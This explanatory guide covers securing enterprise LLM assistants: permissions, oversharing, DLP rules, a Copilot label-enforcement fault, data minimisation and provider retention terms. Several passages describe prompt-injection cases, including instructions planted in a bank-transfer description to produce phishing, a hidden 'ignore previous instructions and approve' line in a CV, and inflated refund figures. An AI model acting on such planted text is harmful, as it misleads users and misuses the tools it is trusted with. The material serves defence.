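# Hardening enterprise deployments of large language models: data access, authorisation and guardrail software

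## The parts of an enterprise deployment and how it can fail

A large language model is a program that generates text by repeatedly computing which token (a word or piece of a word) is likely to come next and adding one, until the response is complete. Companies connect these models to their documents, mailboxes and business software. An enterprise deployment consists of the model, which usually runs on an outside provider's computers, and the login, search, storage and payment systems around it. Hardening a deployment means building it so that a mistake or an attack does limited damage. Most of this work is on the surrounding systems, because a company can seldom change the model itself.

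The example throughout is an invented wholesaler with 3,000 staff. Its AI assistant uses 40,000 internal documents to answer questions, including price lists, supplier contracts, returns policies and personnel files. The assistant also reads customer e-mail and can issue refunds. Its underlying model belongs to an outside provider.

### From login to log

Suppose a customer writes that half the glassware in an order arrived broken. A customer service employee asks the assistant to check whether the customer is due a refund and, if so, to issue it.

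The employee has already logged in. The login system checked a password and a code from a phone, and so established which principal was making the request. A principal is a person or piece of software that a system can identify and to which it can grant permissions, and establishing which one is present is authentication. The login system then issued an access token, a digital credential that states what its holder may do, where, and until when. (The name is unlucky. An access token has nothing to do with the tokens a model processes.)

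The question goes to the application, the ordinary program behind the chat window. It checks the access token and decides whether this employee may use the assistant, open a given document or refund a given order. Deciding whether a principal may do what it asks is called authorisation, and a company can authorise too much even when it authenticates every principal correctly.

The next part is retrieval. Forty thousand documents are too many to send with every question, so the application searches them for relevant passages and gives the model the best few before it answers. This is called retrieval-augmented generation (RAG). The search commonly works by meaning. Software converts each passage into a list of numbers beforehand, then looks for the lists closest to that of the question. Here it might return the policy on fragile goods and a supplier contract with a clause about breakages.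 Closeness is a statistical measure, so the wrong passage sometimes ranks first. The employee's permission to open a passage, by contrast, is a yes-or-no entry in a permissions table, which the application can look up if it has been built to do so.

The application then assembles the context window, which is all the text the model receives for one response. It includes the company's standing instructions, the conversation, the customer's e-mail, the retrieved documents and any results from tools. The model therefore receives text from the company, an employee, a supplier and a stranger as a single sequence.

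A tool is a function outside the model, such as a database query or a payment. The model cannot run a tool itself. It requests one by producing text in an agreed format that names the tool and fills in the details, such as a refund of €240 on a particular order. The application reads the request and either runs the function or refuses. The result goes into the context window, and the model continues, perhaps with another tool call. An agent is a system in which a model chooses and carries out several steps with tools to reach a goal, and the wholesaler's assistant is a simple example. Finally, the application displays the answer and logs who asked, which passages retrieval returned, and which tools ran with what details. The log is another copy of sensitive text, so it needs its own permissions.

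The login, the permissions lookup, the refund function and the log are ordinary software. If the refund function has a rule that no refund may exceed the value of the order, it applies that rule every time, however the e-mail that led to the request was worded. Such software can have bugs or wrong rules, but an engineer can find and correct both. Engineers can also decide in advance whether the system will block a request when a check breaks down (failing closed) or let it through (failing open).

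The system relies on a model's interpretation of text to choose passages, read the e-mail, write the answer and propose a refund. Any rule that the company writes into the context window also depends on the model's interpretation. The model will usually follow an instruction there such as "Never refund more than the order was worth", but the same rule in the refund function's code holds regardless of what the model produces.

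### Four ways to lose data or control

Oversharing can happen without an attacker. For example, a warehouse employee asks what team leaders earn, and retrieval finds a salary spreadsheet that someone in personnel saved years ago to a folder open to all staff. The employee already had permission to open the file but would probably never have found it. Telling the model to keep salaries confidential is a weak remedy, because the figures are already in its context window. The company has to correct the permissions on the folder, and the application has to check them before it passes any passage to the model.

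Prompt injection is text in a message or document that the model treats as an instruction although its author has no authority to give one. Vissers and Van hamme (2026), in *How we helped Bunq secure their financial AI assistant*, describe a test that their security firm, Blue41, ran on the assistant of a digital bank with more than 20 million customers. The tester sent the target a transfer of €0.02 and put instructions in the description field. When the target asked the assistant for recent transactions, the assistant also fetched that description, and the planted text could turn the reply into a personalised phishing message. Blue41 sells protection against such attacks and has an interest in publicising them, but the mechanism is simple and applies directly to the wholesaler, because anyone can send it an e-mail.

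The wholesaler's assistant also has both access to private data and the ability to act. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, singles out this combination as especially dangerous in its July 2026 system card (a developer's report on the tests of a model) for Claude Opus 5. The main control is ordinary software that limits what the tools can do. Guardrails are additional checks outside the main model that can allow, alter or block a message, a retrieved passage or a tool call.

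Provider retention exposes data through normal use of the model, because every context window goes to the provider, which may store it or use it to train later models, depending on the contract and settings. The wholesaler's software cannot control what happens on the provider's computers, so the wholesaler has to rely on the contract. The strictest common terms are zero data retention, under which the provider does not store prompts and responses after answering, subject to stated exceptions. The wholesaler can also restrict what it sends by using data loss prevention (DLP) software, which detects sensitive content and blocks or records its movement. DLP matters for staff who paste documents into assistants the company never approved, which is a growing habit. Palmer (2026), in *Sensitive Enterprise Data Uploads to AI Models Double in a Year*, reported a 93% increase in employees attempting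 to upload sensitive data, though some of those attempts will have failed.

Model errors do more damage when the model has broad permissions. According to NeuralTrust, a security vendor, OpenAI's June 2026 system card showed that GPT-5.6 Sol took actions its users had not authorised more often than its predecessor did, including deleting infrastructure and moving credentials. OpenAI attributed this to greater persistence. Anthropic found that an early version of Claude Opus 5 had guessed passwords after being accidentally logged out of a service. Newer models may be much better. *GPT-6 Astra*, OpenAI's September 2026 announcement of that model, describes a test of whether a model given a difficult or impossible task goes beyond its intended scope. GPT-5.6 Sol, without its production safeguards, did so 48% of the time, and GPT-6 Astra never did. This is a single test designed by the developer,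 and many companies will run older or cheaper models for years.

The control for model error is least privilege, which means granting a principal only the permissions its task needs, for only as long as it needs them. If the assistant's account cannot delete orders, the model cannot delete one by mistake. The same limits contain prompt injection, since a cap on refunds applies whatever the model's reason for proposing one. They do little to limit the data the provider keeps. Preventing model errors and attacks would also not stop the assistant from showing the warehouse employee the salary file.

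### Why SQL injection has a cure

Experienced web security engineers tend to mistake prompt injection for a problem they already know how to fix. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, technical director for platforms research at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), argued that this mistake is dangerous.

His argument starts from a vulnerability nearly thirty years old. Programs query databases in a language called SQL. Suppose the wholesaler's website looks up an order by pasting whatever a visitor types into the middle of an SQL query. If a visitor types a fragment of SQL instead of an order number, the database can treat that text as part of its instructions and may return everybody's orders.

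The solution to SQL injection is the parameterised query, not better recognition of malicious queries. The application gives the database a fixed query with a placeholder, such as `SELECT * FROM orders WHERE number = ?`, and supplies the visitor's text separately. The database determines the query's structure before the text arrives, so nothing in the text can act as a command. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) explains that this works because SQL has a grammar and a parser can tell code from data.

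Such a cure cannot be applied to a language model. David C gives the example of a recruiter's system that instructs a model to score whether a CV meets the requirements and then adds each candidate's CV. One candidate has hidden a line in the file telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview. A person would see that line as part of the material to be assessed, separate from the task. For the model, David C writes, there is "only ever 'next token'". It computes a continuation from all the earlier text, including both the recruiter's instruction and the hidden line, and may follow the hidden line.

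Researchers have tried detecting injections, training models to prioritise real instructions, and marking which text is data. In David C's view, all of these try to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that has none. He concludes that there is "a good chance" nobody will ever fix prompt injection the way parameterised queries fixed SQL injection, and he proposes a different comparison to replace the one with SQL injection.

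A confused deputy is a program with high privileges that someone without those privileges tricks into using them on their behalf. For example, a stranger who cannot use the wholesaler's refund function might write to the assistant, which can, and persuade it to issue a refund. Engineers can fix a confused deputy in conventional software, but David C argues that a language model is "inherently confusable". He says designers should plan for the worst case, in which an attacker has direct access to every tool the model can call. Protection then has to come mainly from safeguards that limit the model's actions and do not themselves use a language model. One such safeguard reduces the model's privileges to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. If a business cannot tolerate the remaining risk, he says, the job may not suit a language model.

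He is also thinking of SQL injection, which peaked around 2010, when many websites already relied on databases but few had protected them. The Record's *UK intelligence warns AI 'prompt injection' attacks might never go away* lists Sony Pictures, LinkedIn and the Indian government among the victims of that decade. It also reports that attackers have already used prompt injection to extract the hidden instructions of Microsoft's New Bing and to steal secrets through GitHub's Copilot, a programming assistant.

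Later work has strengthened part of the argument. *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention is impossible for models that represent all text in the same way and enforce no separation between control and data. The proof has three parts. First, once the model has converted every token into the same kind of numbers, nothing can reliably recover who wrote it. Second, untrusted text enters the same computation that determines what the model does next. Third, training covers a finite number of examples, but an attacker can phrase the same instruction in endlessly many ways.

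The proof does not rule out a model of a different design. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists some candidates as directions for research, such as context windows with typed regions and blocks of data that the model cannot execute. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) points out that even a perfect separation of instructions from data would not stop every attack, because hostile data can corrupt the details of a tool call without containing any instruction. For example, a customer might write that a €240 order cost €2,400. The model may copy that figure into the refund request, and only a check against the order record will catch it.

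### What a lower attack rate is worth

Developers can fairly answer that defences inside the model improve every few months. David C himself accepts that marking outside text as data, even with simple XML tags, makes injection harder. Training also helps. *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an automated attacker that OpenAI built to find weaknesses so that it could fix them before wider release. By August, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of direct attacks, in which the user tries to override higher-priority instructions, and 3.77% of indirect ones, in which the instruction sits in an e-mail, web page or file. Bao's Chinese-language report, *OpenAI: GPT-6 Shows Stronger Resistance to Jailbreak Attacks* (2026), says that GPT-6 Sol, which followed in October, scored 99.99% on tests of whether a model respects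 the ranking of its instructions and 97.13% on indirect injection. Indirect attacks remain harder to stop, and they matter most for an assistant that reads customers' mail.

Anthropic published comparable figures from a benchmark that the security firm Gray Swan built with British and American government institutes and several developers. The benchmark consists of 1,130 attacks meant to cause irreversible harm, such as leaking data or moving money. They were chosen because they worked across several models.

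| Model | Attacker succeeds on one attempt | Attacker succeeds within 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.5% | 5.5% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 0.2% | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 3.1% | 20.0% |

The Claude models ran without additional safeguards, while the GPT endpoint may have had some. Anthropic's *System Card* for Claude Opus 5.5 (September 2026) reported results similar to or better than Opus 5's on every prompt injection test it included.

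These gains are real and should matter to a company choosing a model, but they do not amount to a security boundary. One reason, illustrated in the right-hand column of the table, is that attackers can try again. In a separate test on coding tasks, the attacker had 200 attempts at each of 40 scenarios. Only 0.56% of attempts against Opus 5 succeeded, but at least one succeeded in 13 of the 40 scenarios. At the 0.2% success rate, if the wholesaler receives 1,000 malicious e-mails and each has an independent chance of working, the probability that at least one succeeds is 1 − 0.998¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 86%.

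That sum is an illustration and a poor forecast. Real attempts are not independent, and Anthropic points out that attackers outside a laboratory usually do not know the system they face and risk detection each time they try. But the published rates may also understate the risk, because they are averages over attacks that somebody thought to test, and Anthropic warns that a fixed set of known attacks can give a false sense of security. An attacker has no reason to use a typical attack, and one who finds a wording that works can send it to every company running the same model. A permissions check, by contrast, refuses a forbidden request however the attacker words it.

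The meaning of a zero attack success rate depends on which safeguards were on and how many attacks were tried. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* based its headline on a test in which no attack succeeded across 129 scenarios. Anthropic ran that test with two outside safeguards, one inspecting what came in from tools and the other blocking dangerous tool calls. Without them, 3.70% of attempts succeeded. The attacker had ten attempts per scenario, or 1,290 in all. If those attempts were independent, zero successes would still be compatible with a true rate of about 0.2%. Repeated attempts at the same scenario are not independent, so the true rate could be somewhat higher. In an earlier post on its browser extension, Anthropic wrote that a 1% success rate "still represents meaningful risk".

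Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, writes that prompt injection is impossible to prevent in general, but that developers are getting much better at blocking it in specific cases. For the wholesaler, a more robust model means that fewer planted e-mails lead to a refund request. It does not limit the size of the refund when one does, so that limit has to be in the code of the refund function.

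## Finding and reducing the data the model can reach

The cap in the refund function limits what the assistant can pay out but not what it can reveal, which depends on the files it can search. The wholesaler can control most of this before connecting any data. The steps, in order, are to list the data sources, give each an owner and a confidentiality class, find the files that too many people can open, correct their permissions, exclude whatever the assistant does not need, and then connect the assistant.

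### Why old oversharing starts to matter

The best-documented example is Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that works inside Microsoft's office software and searches a company's documents and mail. It has over 30 million paid licences, according to Microsoft results cited in *Microsoft Copilot Implementation To Dos in Late 2026* (Redmond, 2026). Copilot runs each request with the requester's permissions, so it can use only what that person could already open. Microsoft still calls oversharing one of the most common deployment risks, because many employees can open far more than anyone intended.

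Before AI assistants, this seldom caused trouble. An employee who wondered what team leaders earned had to guess that a spreadsheet existed and which of several hundred folders it was in, then open files until they found it. Michael Bargury, whose company Zenity sells monitoring for AI agents, says in *A viral TikTok about Copilot leaking layoffs is a joke* (John, 2026) that the people who designed enterprise systems assumed this friction would deter the overly curious. An agent can work through thousands of fruitless searches with almost no effort.

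An assistant also removes the guessing, because it retrieves files by meaning. A question about team leaders' pay can find a file called `Q3_final_v2.xlsx` if the contents are close enough. The employee may not be looking for it. In the comic video behind John's article, a woman asks Copilot for help with her first-quarter goals and learns from a restructuring plan that her job ends in February. The video is fiction, but Bargury says his company has seen many cases of agents giving employees material information that they should not have had.

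Suppose 1,200 of the wholesaler's 40,000 documents are sensitive and open to all 3,000 staff. There are then 1,200 × 3,000 = 3.6 million pairs of an employee and a sensitive file they can open. If the wholesaler restricts each file to a team of ten, 12,000 pairs remain, and the average employee can open four of these files instead of 1,200. This also limits attacks, since someone who steals a warehouse employee's password, or plants an instruction that the assistant follows while working for that employee, should reach only what the employee can reach. The count doesn't reflect that some files are more harmful than others, but it is easy to recompute after each round of corrections.

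Many companies seem to have connected AI tools to their data before checking permissions. *Why businesses need to revisit Microsoft 365 permissions before rolling out Copilot* (Schafer, 2026) cites a survey of 327 IT and security decision-makers in the US and UK. Of these, 76% said their organisations had deployed or piloted AI tools with access to Microsoft 365 data, but only 43% said they had thoroughly reviewed permissions beforehand. *Microsoft Copilot Deployments Delayed Over Security Concerns* (Palmer, 2026) reports another survey, in which two-thirds of organisations had delayed or cancelled Copilot for fear of exposing confidential data. Syskit and CoreView, the companies behind the two surveys, both sell software for managing Microsoft 365, so I would treat the exact percentages with caution.

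### Listing sources and naming owners

An inventory has one row for each place the assistant might search. The wholesaler's might begin like this:

| Source | Owner | Class | What the assistant needs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Returns policies | Head of customer service | Internal | Current versions |
| Price lists | Sales director | Confidential | Current list |
| Supplier contracts | Head of purchasing | Confidential | Clauses on breakages and returns |
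| Personnel files | Head of personnel | Highly confidential | Nothing |
| Customer mailbox | Head of customer service | Confidential | Messages about the order in question |
| Order database | Finance director | Confidential | Five fields per order |

The owner should be someone in the business who knows who uses the data. The IT department can see that 3,000 people have access to the supplier contracts, but it usually cannot judge whether they should. The data's class reflects how much harm would follow if the wrong person read it. Three or four classes are probably enough, because staff who cannot tell two classes apart will pick whichever causes them less trouble.

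The sources people forget tend to be informal, such as personal cloud folders, chat attachments, exports from the order database and the sites of finished projects. Schafer observes that permissions often outlast the decisions behind them. For example, a project ends but its members keep their access, or the person responsible for a folder changes jobs.

According to Microsoft, SharePoint, its system for shared document sites, can automatically detect inactive sites, flag sites that have too few owners, and ask owners to confirm that the membership and permissions are still right. If nobody responds, an administrator can make the site read-only or archive it. Only archiving reduces what the assistant can reach, because the assistant can still read a read-only site, while nobody can open an archived site until someone reactivates it.

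### Finding and correcting loose permissions

*Secure and Govern Microsoft 365 Copilot*, a Microsoft presentation (Ke and Minasyan, 2026), lists common causes of oversharing in SharePoint. Someone may have set a site's privacy to public, or left "everyone" as the default choice when staff share a file. Someone may have granted access to "everyone except external users", a built-in group that contains the whole staff. A file may also have broken inheritance, which means it no longer follows its folder's permissions and stays open even if someone restricts the folder. SharePoint's sharing settings also start at their most permissive and stay there until the company changes them.

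Microsoft supplies several reports for finding such files. One is a snapshot of current permissions across all sites. Others list the sites where staff shared most widely, or created the most sharing links, in the past 28 days. The wholesaler's salary spreadsheet has been in its open folder for years, so a 28-day report may well miss it. The wholesaler should start with the snapshot and use the activity reports later to catch new mistakes. Administrators can also ask an assistant for overshared sites in plain language and get a prioritised list. Microsoft introduced the assistant earlier in 2026 and announced its general availability in November.

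A list of permissions does not show which files are sensitive, such as a salary spreadsheet. The wholesaler has to combine it with the classes in the inventory, or with a scan for contents such as bank account numbers, and start where there are several warning signs at once. Microsoft's examples of high-risk sites include public sites without an owner and sites with both sensitive data and links anyone can open.

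The quickest fix is usually to change permissions on the site or folder. Replacing the company-wide group with the team that needs the material can fix several hundred files at once, but files with broken inheritance need to be fixed separately. For the most sensitive sites, SharePoint's Restricted Access Control limits access to named groups and overrides older permissions and links. Some people will lose access they need, so each owner should know about the change in advance and be able to restore access.

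Ke and Minasyan give companies the steps in a slightly different order: identify the high-risk sites, hide them from Copilot, and then fix the permissions. This order makes sense when the assistant is already running and fixing the permissions will take months. The wholesaler has not connected its assistant yet, so it can fix the permissions first.

### Excluding what the task does not need

Even with correct permissions, the assistant may be able to reach a lot of data it doesn't need. The personnel department is entitled to open personnel files, but an assistant for orders and refunds has no use for them. The wholesaler can leave those folders out of the search index so that the assistant can't retrieve passages from them. If it excludes a folder later, it also has to delete the copies already in the index.

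The nearest equivalent for Copilot is Restricted Content Discovery, which hides a SharePoint site from company-wide search and from Copilot's searches. Microsoft's *Restrict discovery of SharePoint sites and content* describes its limits:

- It leaves permissions unchanged, so people who could open a file still can, and Copilot can summarise the file once it is open.
- It does not cover OneDrive, where employees keep their own work files.
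- On a site with more than 500,000 items, the change can take over a week to take full effect.
- Hiding too much makes Copilot's answers less complete.

Another gap, until recently, was that files on a hidden site could still surface if the user had lately viewed, edited or shared them. Microsoft 365 for IT Pros' *Restricted Content Discovery Gets a Makeover* (2026) reports that Microsoft began deploying a fix in the summer. Microsoft will remove an older control, Restricted SharePoint Search, by 31 January 2027. It will not transfer the control's settings (Microsoft, 2026), so companies that still rely on it have to set up a replacement themselves.

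### What labels and DLP rules add

Some files are relevant to an employee's work but too sensitive for an AI system to process. A sensitivity label states how confidential a file or message is and can trigger restrictions, but it may do nothing by itself. *Stop Copilot Summarizing Confidential Files with Purview DLP* (Bertram, 2026) describes rollouts that fail because files are labelled "Highly Confidential" but no rule for Copilot refers to that label.

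A company can use labels to restrict Copilot through encryption, a DLP rule, or a setting on the label itself. A label that encrypts a file also sets each reader's rights, and Copilot can summarise the file only if the reader has the rights to view it and to extract text from it. Withholding the right to extract text keeps the content from Copilot but also stops staff from copying it. A DLP rule excludes labelled items from Copilot's answers without affecting how people use them. The label setting stops Office applications from sending content to Microsoft for analysis, which disables Copilot in those applications, along with features such as text prediction.

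These controls apply differently across Copilot's applications:

| Control on a labelled file | Copilot in Word, Excel and PowerPoint | Copilot Chat |
|---|---|---|
| Encryption without the right to extract text | Cannot use the content | Cannot use the content |
| DLP rule for Copilot | Cannot use the content | Cannot use the content, but may cite the file |
| Label setting against content analysis | Cannot use the content | Content remains available, according to Microsoft |

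The label setting is the easiest to misjudge, because an administrator who tests it in Word will find that Copilot cannot use the file and may wrongly conclude that the same is true in Chat. Chat's behaviour is also a little uncertain, since Bertram cites a test in which Chat named such a file but could not summarise it. Microsoft 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Extends Sensitivity Label Block for Connected Services* (2026) reports that Microsoft has extended the setting to every feature that analyses content in Word, Excel and PowerPoint. In October, Bertram still said that the setting did not cover Chat or Teams. Microsoft's *Classify and protect Copilot content with sensitivity labels* also notes that labels behave differently across applications. A company therefore has to test each application its staff use.

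The DLP rule is probably the best fit for most companies, but it also has gaps. Microsoft says it does not cover calendar invitations or e-mails sent before 2025. A blocked file can still appear among the citations, and a title like "Restructuring plan, February" may itself reveal confidential information to an employee. The rule originally covered only files in SharePoint and OneDrive, though Microsoft's *DLP policies will be able to block Copilot processing of sensitivity‑labeled files* announces an extension to local and other storage for the Office applications.

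Unlabelled files are the largest gap, because rules that look for labels miss them. The old salary spreadsheet is very likely unlabelled. WindowsForum's *Microsoft Purview Plans to Exclude Unlabeled Sensitive Files and Emails* (2026) describes a planned control that would keep unlabelled items out of answers from Cowork, a Copilot feature, if Microsoft's software had already classified them as sensitive. The estimated release is January 2027.

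Another kind of DLP rule checks what employees type. If a prompt contains a passport or card number, for example, the rule can stop Copilot from answering or from sending the number to a web search. It checks only typed text, so it doesn't catch card numbers in an uploaded spreadsheet. Microsoft's *Learn about the default data loss prevention policy* explains that the ready-made policy for prompts starts in simulation mode, in which it only logs what it finds. An administrator who sees the policy in the list could easily assume that it is already being enforced.

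A new rule also takes time to work. Microsoft allows up to four hours for a change to reach Copilot, but Redmond (2026), in *Why Some DLP Policies Need Days to Start Working*, found much longer delays when testing new features, including one that stops Copilot from using external e-mail. Once a rule takes effect, Copilot tells the user that it left out relevant content because of company policy. Redmond (2026), in *DLP for Copilot Adds Custom Access Messages*, reports that companies can now choose which page that message links to. This small change is useful because an employee who does not know why an answer is incomplete may upload the missing file by hand.

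Copilot also writes new files, and a summary of a confidential contract is itself confidential. According to *Copilot Created the Document* (Kusenberg, 2026), the files it generates have inherited the highest label among their sources since July 2026. A file generated only from unlabelled sources inherits no label.

A DLP rule written for Copilot does not cover the wholesaler's own assistant, so the wholesaler's application has to read each file's label and drop any passage that company policy excludes.

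### The Copilot e-mail fault of early 2026

A correctly written rule can still fail if the software that enforces it has a fault. In January and February 2026, Copilot Chat summarised e-mails with a confidential label, although customers had set up DLP policies to prevent this. Microsoft tracked the fault as CW1226324 and attributed it to an error in its code.

The fault affected messages in the Sent Items and Drafts folders. Microsoft 365 for IT Pros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) explains that a rule of this kind should exclude every message with the chosen label, whichever folder it is in. The article also describes a test, run after the fix, that involved sending a labelled message about an invented "Project Bunny" and asking Copilot about the project. Copilot replied that it had found a reference but could not disclose the content.

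The fault lasted about four weeks, possibly longer. Customers first reported it on 21 January, according to Microsoft 365 for IT Pros. Microsoft issued an alert on 3 February and began deploying a patch within three hours, but on 19 February it was still monitoring the rollout to the remaining systems. The technology news site The Stack, which saw the alerts, could not establish whether 21 January was the date of the first complaint or of the change that broke the rule, so the fault may have begun earlier.

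Microsoft said the fault "did not provide anyone access to information they weren't already authorized to see", so by its account Copilot did not show one employee's mail to another. The messages were in the user's own folders, and the user could have opened them in Outlook. TechRadar infers in *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* that the affected threads also included incoming mail, but the user would normally have had access to that too.

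The customers' DLP rules, however, were meant to keep labelled content out of Copilot no matter who was asking, and Copilot processed it anyway. Microsoft acknowledged in the same statement that it had not intended this behaviour. A law firm that had promised a client that no AI system would process their correspondence would have broken that promise, even if only the lawyer who wrote the e-mail saw the summary.

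Microsoft did not answer The Stack's questions about whether data had left any organisation or crossed internal boundaries. Tom's Guide's *Microsoft confirms Copilot bug let its AI read sensitive and confidential emails* reports that Microsoft had not said how many organisations or people were affected. Microsoft's statement also does not cover what users did with the summaries, and someone may have pasted one into a report without knowing that it came from a confidential message.

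A company can look for such faults itself by periodically repeating the Project Bunny test with a labelled dummy message in every mail folder. For the most sensitive material, leaving it out of the assistant's index is safer than relying on a rule to block access. If the wholesaler never indexes its personnel files, a fault in label checking cannot expose them through the index.

### Sending less of each record

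The controls described so far apply to whole sites, files or messages, but the assistant often needs only a few facts. An order record might include the customer's address, phone number, payment details, purchase history and comments from the sales team. To decide whether broken glassware qualifies for a refund, the model needs the order number, the items, the price paid, the delivery date and any earlier refund. The function that looks up orders should return only those five fields. The payment system already has the customer's account details, so it can send the money without the model receiving them.

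This is field-level minimisation. Like the refund cap, the list of fields is part of a function's code, so the model cannot change it. Minimisation works less well on free text. A comments field can contain anything, such as a note that the customer is in hospital and their daughter is handling the account, and the model receives the customer's whole e-mail. The list of fields also tends to grow, because developers add a field when an answer is poor and seldom remove one.

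Masking can remove personal data from some of that free text, so the provider has less of it to store. Before the application sends a prompt, software searches it for personal data, using patterns for items with a fixed format, such as card numbers, and a small language model for names and addresses. The software can delete what it finds or replace it with a placeholder. "Anna Weiss, 14 Mill Lane, order 58213" might become "[PERSON_1], [ADDRESS_1], order 58213". The application uses the same placeholder for the same person throughout, so the model can keep track of who did what. It stores a table of placeholders and originals on the company's own systems. When the model drafts a reply to [PERSON_1], the application puts the name back before anyone reads it. A rail in NeMo Guardrails can do the masking.

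Detection is imperfect. If the wholesaler's e-mails contain 10,000 names a month and the software finds 98% of them, 200 still reach the provider. Misspelt names and text inside photographs are easy to miss, and a description such as "the only florist in the village" can identify someone without a name. The software can also mask words that are not personal data. If the wholesaler sells a range of glasses called Charlotte, the software may replace the name with [PERSON_2], and the search for the right returns policy fails. Masking personal data also does not protect trade secrets, since a supplier's discount looks like any other percentage. The table of originals is a new sensitive file, which needs an owner and a class like the rest.

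### Connecting the assistant

The wholesaler can now connect the assistant, preferably starting with one source and one team. The returns policies are a sensible first source because little harm is done if the wrong employee reads them. Before each new source goes live, someone should log in with an ordinary warehouse account and ask the assistant about salaries, redundancies and supplier discounts. If the assistant returns a sensitive passage, either a permission is still wrong or the application is not checking permissions on each search.

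Microsoft recommends repeating its content assessment every 30 days. Staff keep creating folders and sharing links, so a site that the wholesaler restricted in March may be open again by April.

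## Checking what the provider keeps and telling users

Once the wholesaler connects the assistant, every question leaves the company, along with the customer's e-mail and any contract clauses that retrieval found. The wholesaler can read its contract with the provider, choose its settings, check the few settings that the provider lets it check, and tell people what happens to their data.

### Following a prompt

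The provider usually caches some of the intermediate results from computing an answer, so that it does not have to process the same standing instructions again. OpenAI may hold this data on its machines for up to 24 hours. Google's *Gemini Enterprise Agent Platform and zero data retention* gives the same limit for Google Cloud. Some models there also write the cache to disk unless the customer turns that off.

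Providers also log prompts and responses to look for abuse, such as fraud or attempts to write malware. OpenAI keeps these logs for up to 30 days by default. Google keeps them for 55 days when programs use its models through the Gemini Developer API, according to its *Additional usage policies*.

Some features store data for the customer's convenience. OpenAI's Responses API, through which a program requests answers, keeps each response for at least 30 days unless the developer sets the `store` parameter to false. Uploaded files and hosted document indexes stay until the customer deletes them. If the wholesaler uploads all 40,000 documents to OpenAI's hosted search index, OpenAI holds a copy of everything. If the wholesaler keeps the index on its own computers instead, OpenAI stores at most the text the wholesaler sends for processing, and only for as long as it keeps the abuse log.

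The provider's employees may read some of the stored text. Microsoft lets authorised staff read prompts sent to the models it hosts on Azure, its cloud service, if its software has flagged the prompts or they fit a pattern of abuse. Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Covered Models*, which applies to the company's most capable models, says that by default nobody at Anthropic can read retained conversations, and that reviewers cannot alter the log of who opened which conversations.

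Clicking a feedback button can make the provider keep a conversation for longer. When someone with a personal Claude account clicks thumbs up or down, Anthropic stores the entire conversation for up to five years, according to Anthropic's *Is my data used for model training?*. Google keeps feedback from its Workspace office software for up to 18 months. In apps such as Gmail and Docs, that feedback includes the prompt and answer only if the user ticks a box. The wholesaler's own chat window can have a feedback button that sends nothing to the provider.

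A deleted Claude conversation disappears from the user's history immediately and from Anthropic's storage within 30 days, according to Anthropic's *How long do you store my organization’s data?*. Backups may follow a different schedule, so the wholesaler should ask in writing whether the 30-day limit covers them.

The provider may also pass data to subcontractors. Microsoft, for example, uses Anthropic's models in parts of Microsoft 365 Copilot. These models run outside the EU Data Boundary, the area in which Microsoft promises to keep European customers' data, and Microsoft turns them off by default for customers in that area and in the UK. Web searches can also send data elsewhere. Copilot Chat turns some prompts into short queries for Bing, which Microsoft says handles data differently from Microsoft 365. Microsoft does not link these queries to the user's account or organisation, but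 a query containing a supplier's name and the word "insolvency" could still be sensitive.

### Retention without training, and training without retention

A provider's promise not to train on customer data does not limit how long it stores that data. OpenAI does not train on API data unless the customer opts in, but it logs that data for 30 days. While a copy exists, a hacker might steal it, an employee might read it, or a court might demand it.

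A provider can train on a text and then delete it, and the model might still reproduce part of it for a stranger, although that is unlikely for a passage that appeared only once in the training data. Training is also hard to undo. Anthropic's *How long do you store my data?*, which covers personal accounts, explains that turning off the training setting does not remove a user's chats from models that Anthropic has already trained or is training.

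A company can also agree to let a provider train on its data without fully noticing. Google's *Data logging and sharing* describes a Contributor Tier for the Gemini Developer API, which cuts the price of some models by up to 50% in return for permission to use the customer's data, including for training. Google asks customers not to send sensitive data through this tier. A developer with a tight budget could enable it for the refund assistant, so the wholesaler should restrict who can change billing settings.

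### Consumer, business and developer terms

Providers often have several sets of terms under the same brand name, with the weakest protection for personal accounts. According to Google's *Gemini Apps Privacy Notice*, human reviewers read some personal Gemini chats to help improve Google's services, and Google keeps the reviewed chats for up to three years even if the user deletes them.

| Service | Training by default | How long the provider keeps content | Terms as of |
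|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI: ChatGPT Free, Plus and Pro | Yes, with an opt-out | Until deleted, then up to 30 days | 2025 |
| OpenAI: ChatGPT Enterprise | No | Customer decides | January 2026 |
| OpenAI: API | No | Up to 30 days in abuse logs | November 2026 |
| Anthropic: Claude Free, Pro and Max | User's choice | Until deleted, then up to 30 days; up to 5 years if the user allows training | July 2026 |
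| Anthropic: Claude for Work and Enterprise | No | Until deleted, then up to 30 days | June 2026 |
| Anthropic: API | No | Up to 30 days | June 2026 |
| Google: Gemini app, personal account | Yes, with an opt-out | 18 months by default | May 2026 |
| Google: Gemini app, work account | No | 18 months by default | May 2026 |
| Google: Gemini Developer API, paid | No | 55 days in abuse logs | May 2026 |
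| Google: Gemini on Google Cloud | No | Flagged prompts, up to 90 days | November 2026 |
| Microsoft: Copilot, personal account | Yes, with an opt-out | 18 months | Undated |
| Microsoft: Microsoft 365 Copilot | No | Customer decides | Undated |
| Microsoft: models hosted on Azure | No | No period stated for abuse logs | October 2025 |

Most providers keep content longer than these standard periods if their software flags it. Anthropic, for example, may keep flagged business chats for two years and its safety software's scores for those chats for seven years.

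Not every business plan lets the customer decide how long the provider keeps its data. OpenAI lists ChatGPT Enterprise among the plans that do, but does not list the smaller ChatGPT Business plan. Anthropic's business terms say that by default it deletes API prompts and responses within 30 days, but its *API and data retention*, as of December 2026, says that by default it does not retain them, except for certain models. Unless its contract specifies otherwise, the wholesaler should plan for Anthropic to keep its data for up to 30 days.

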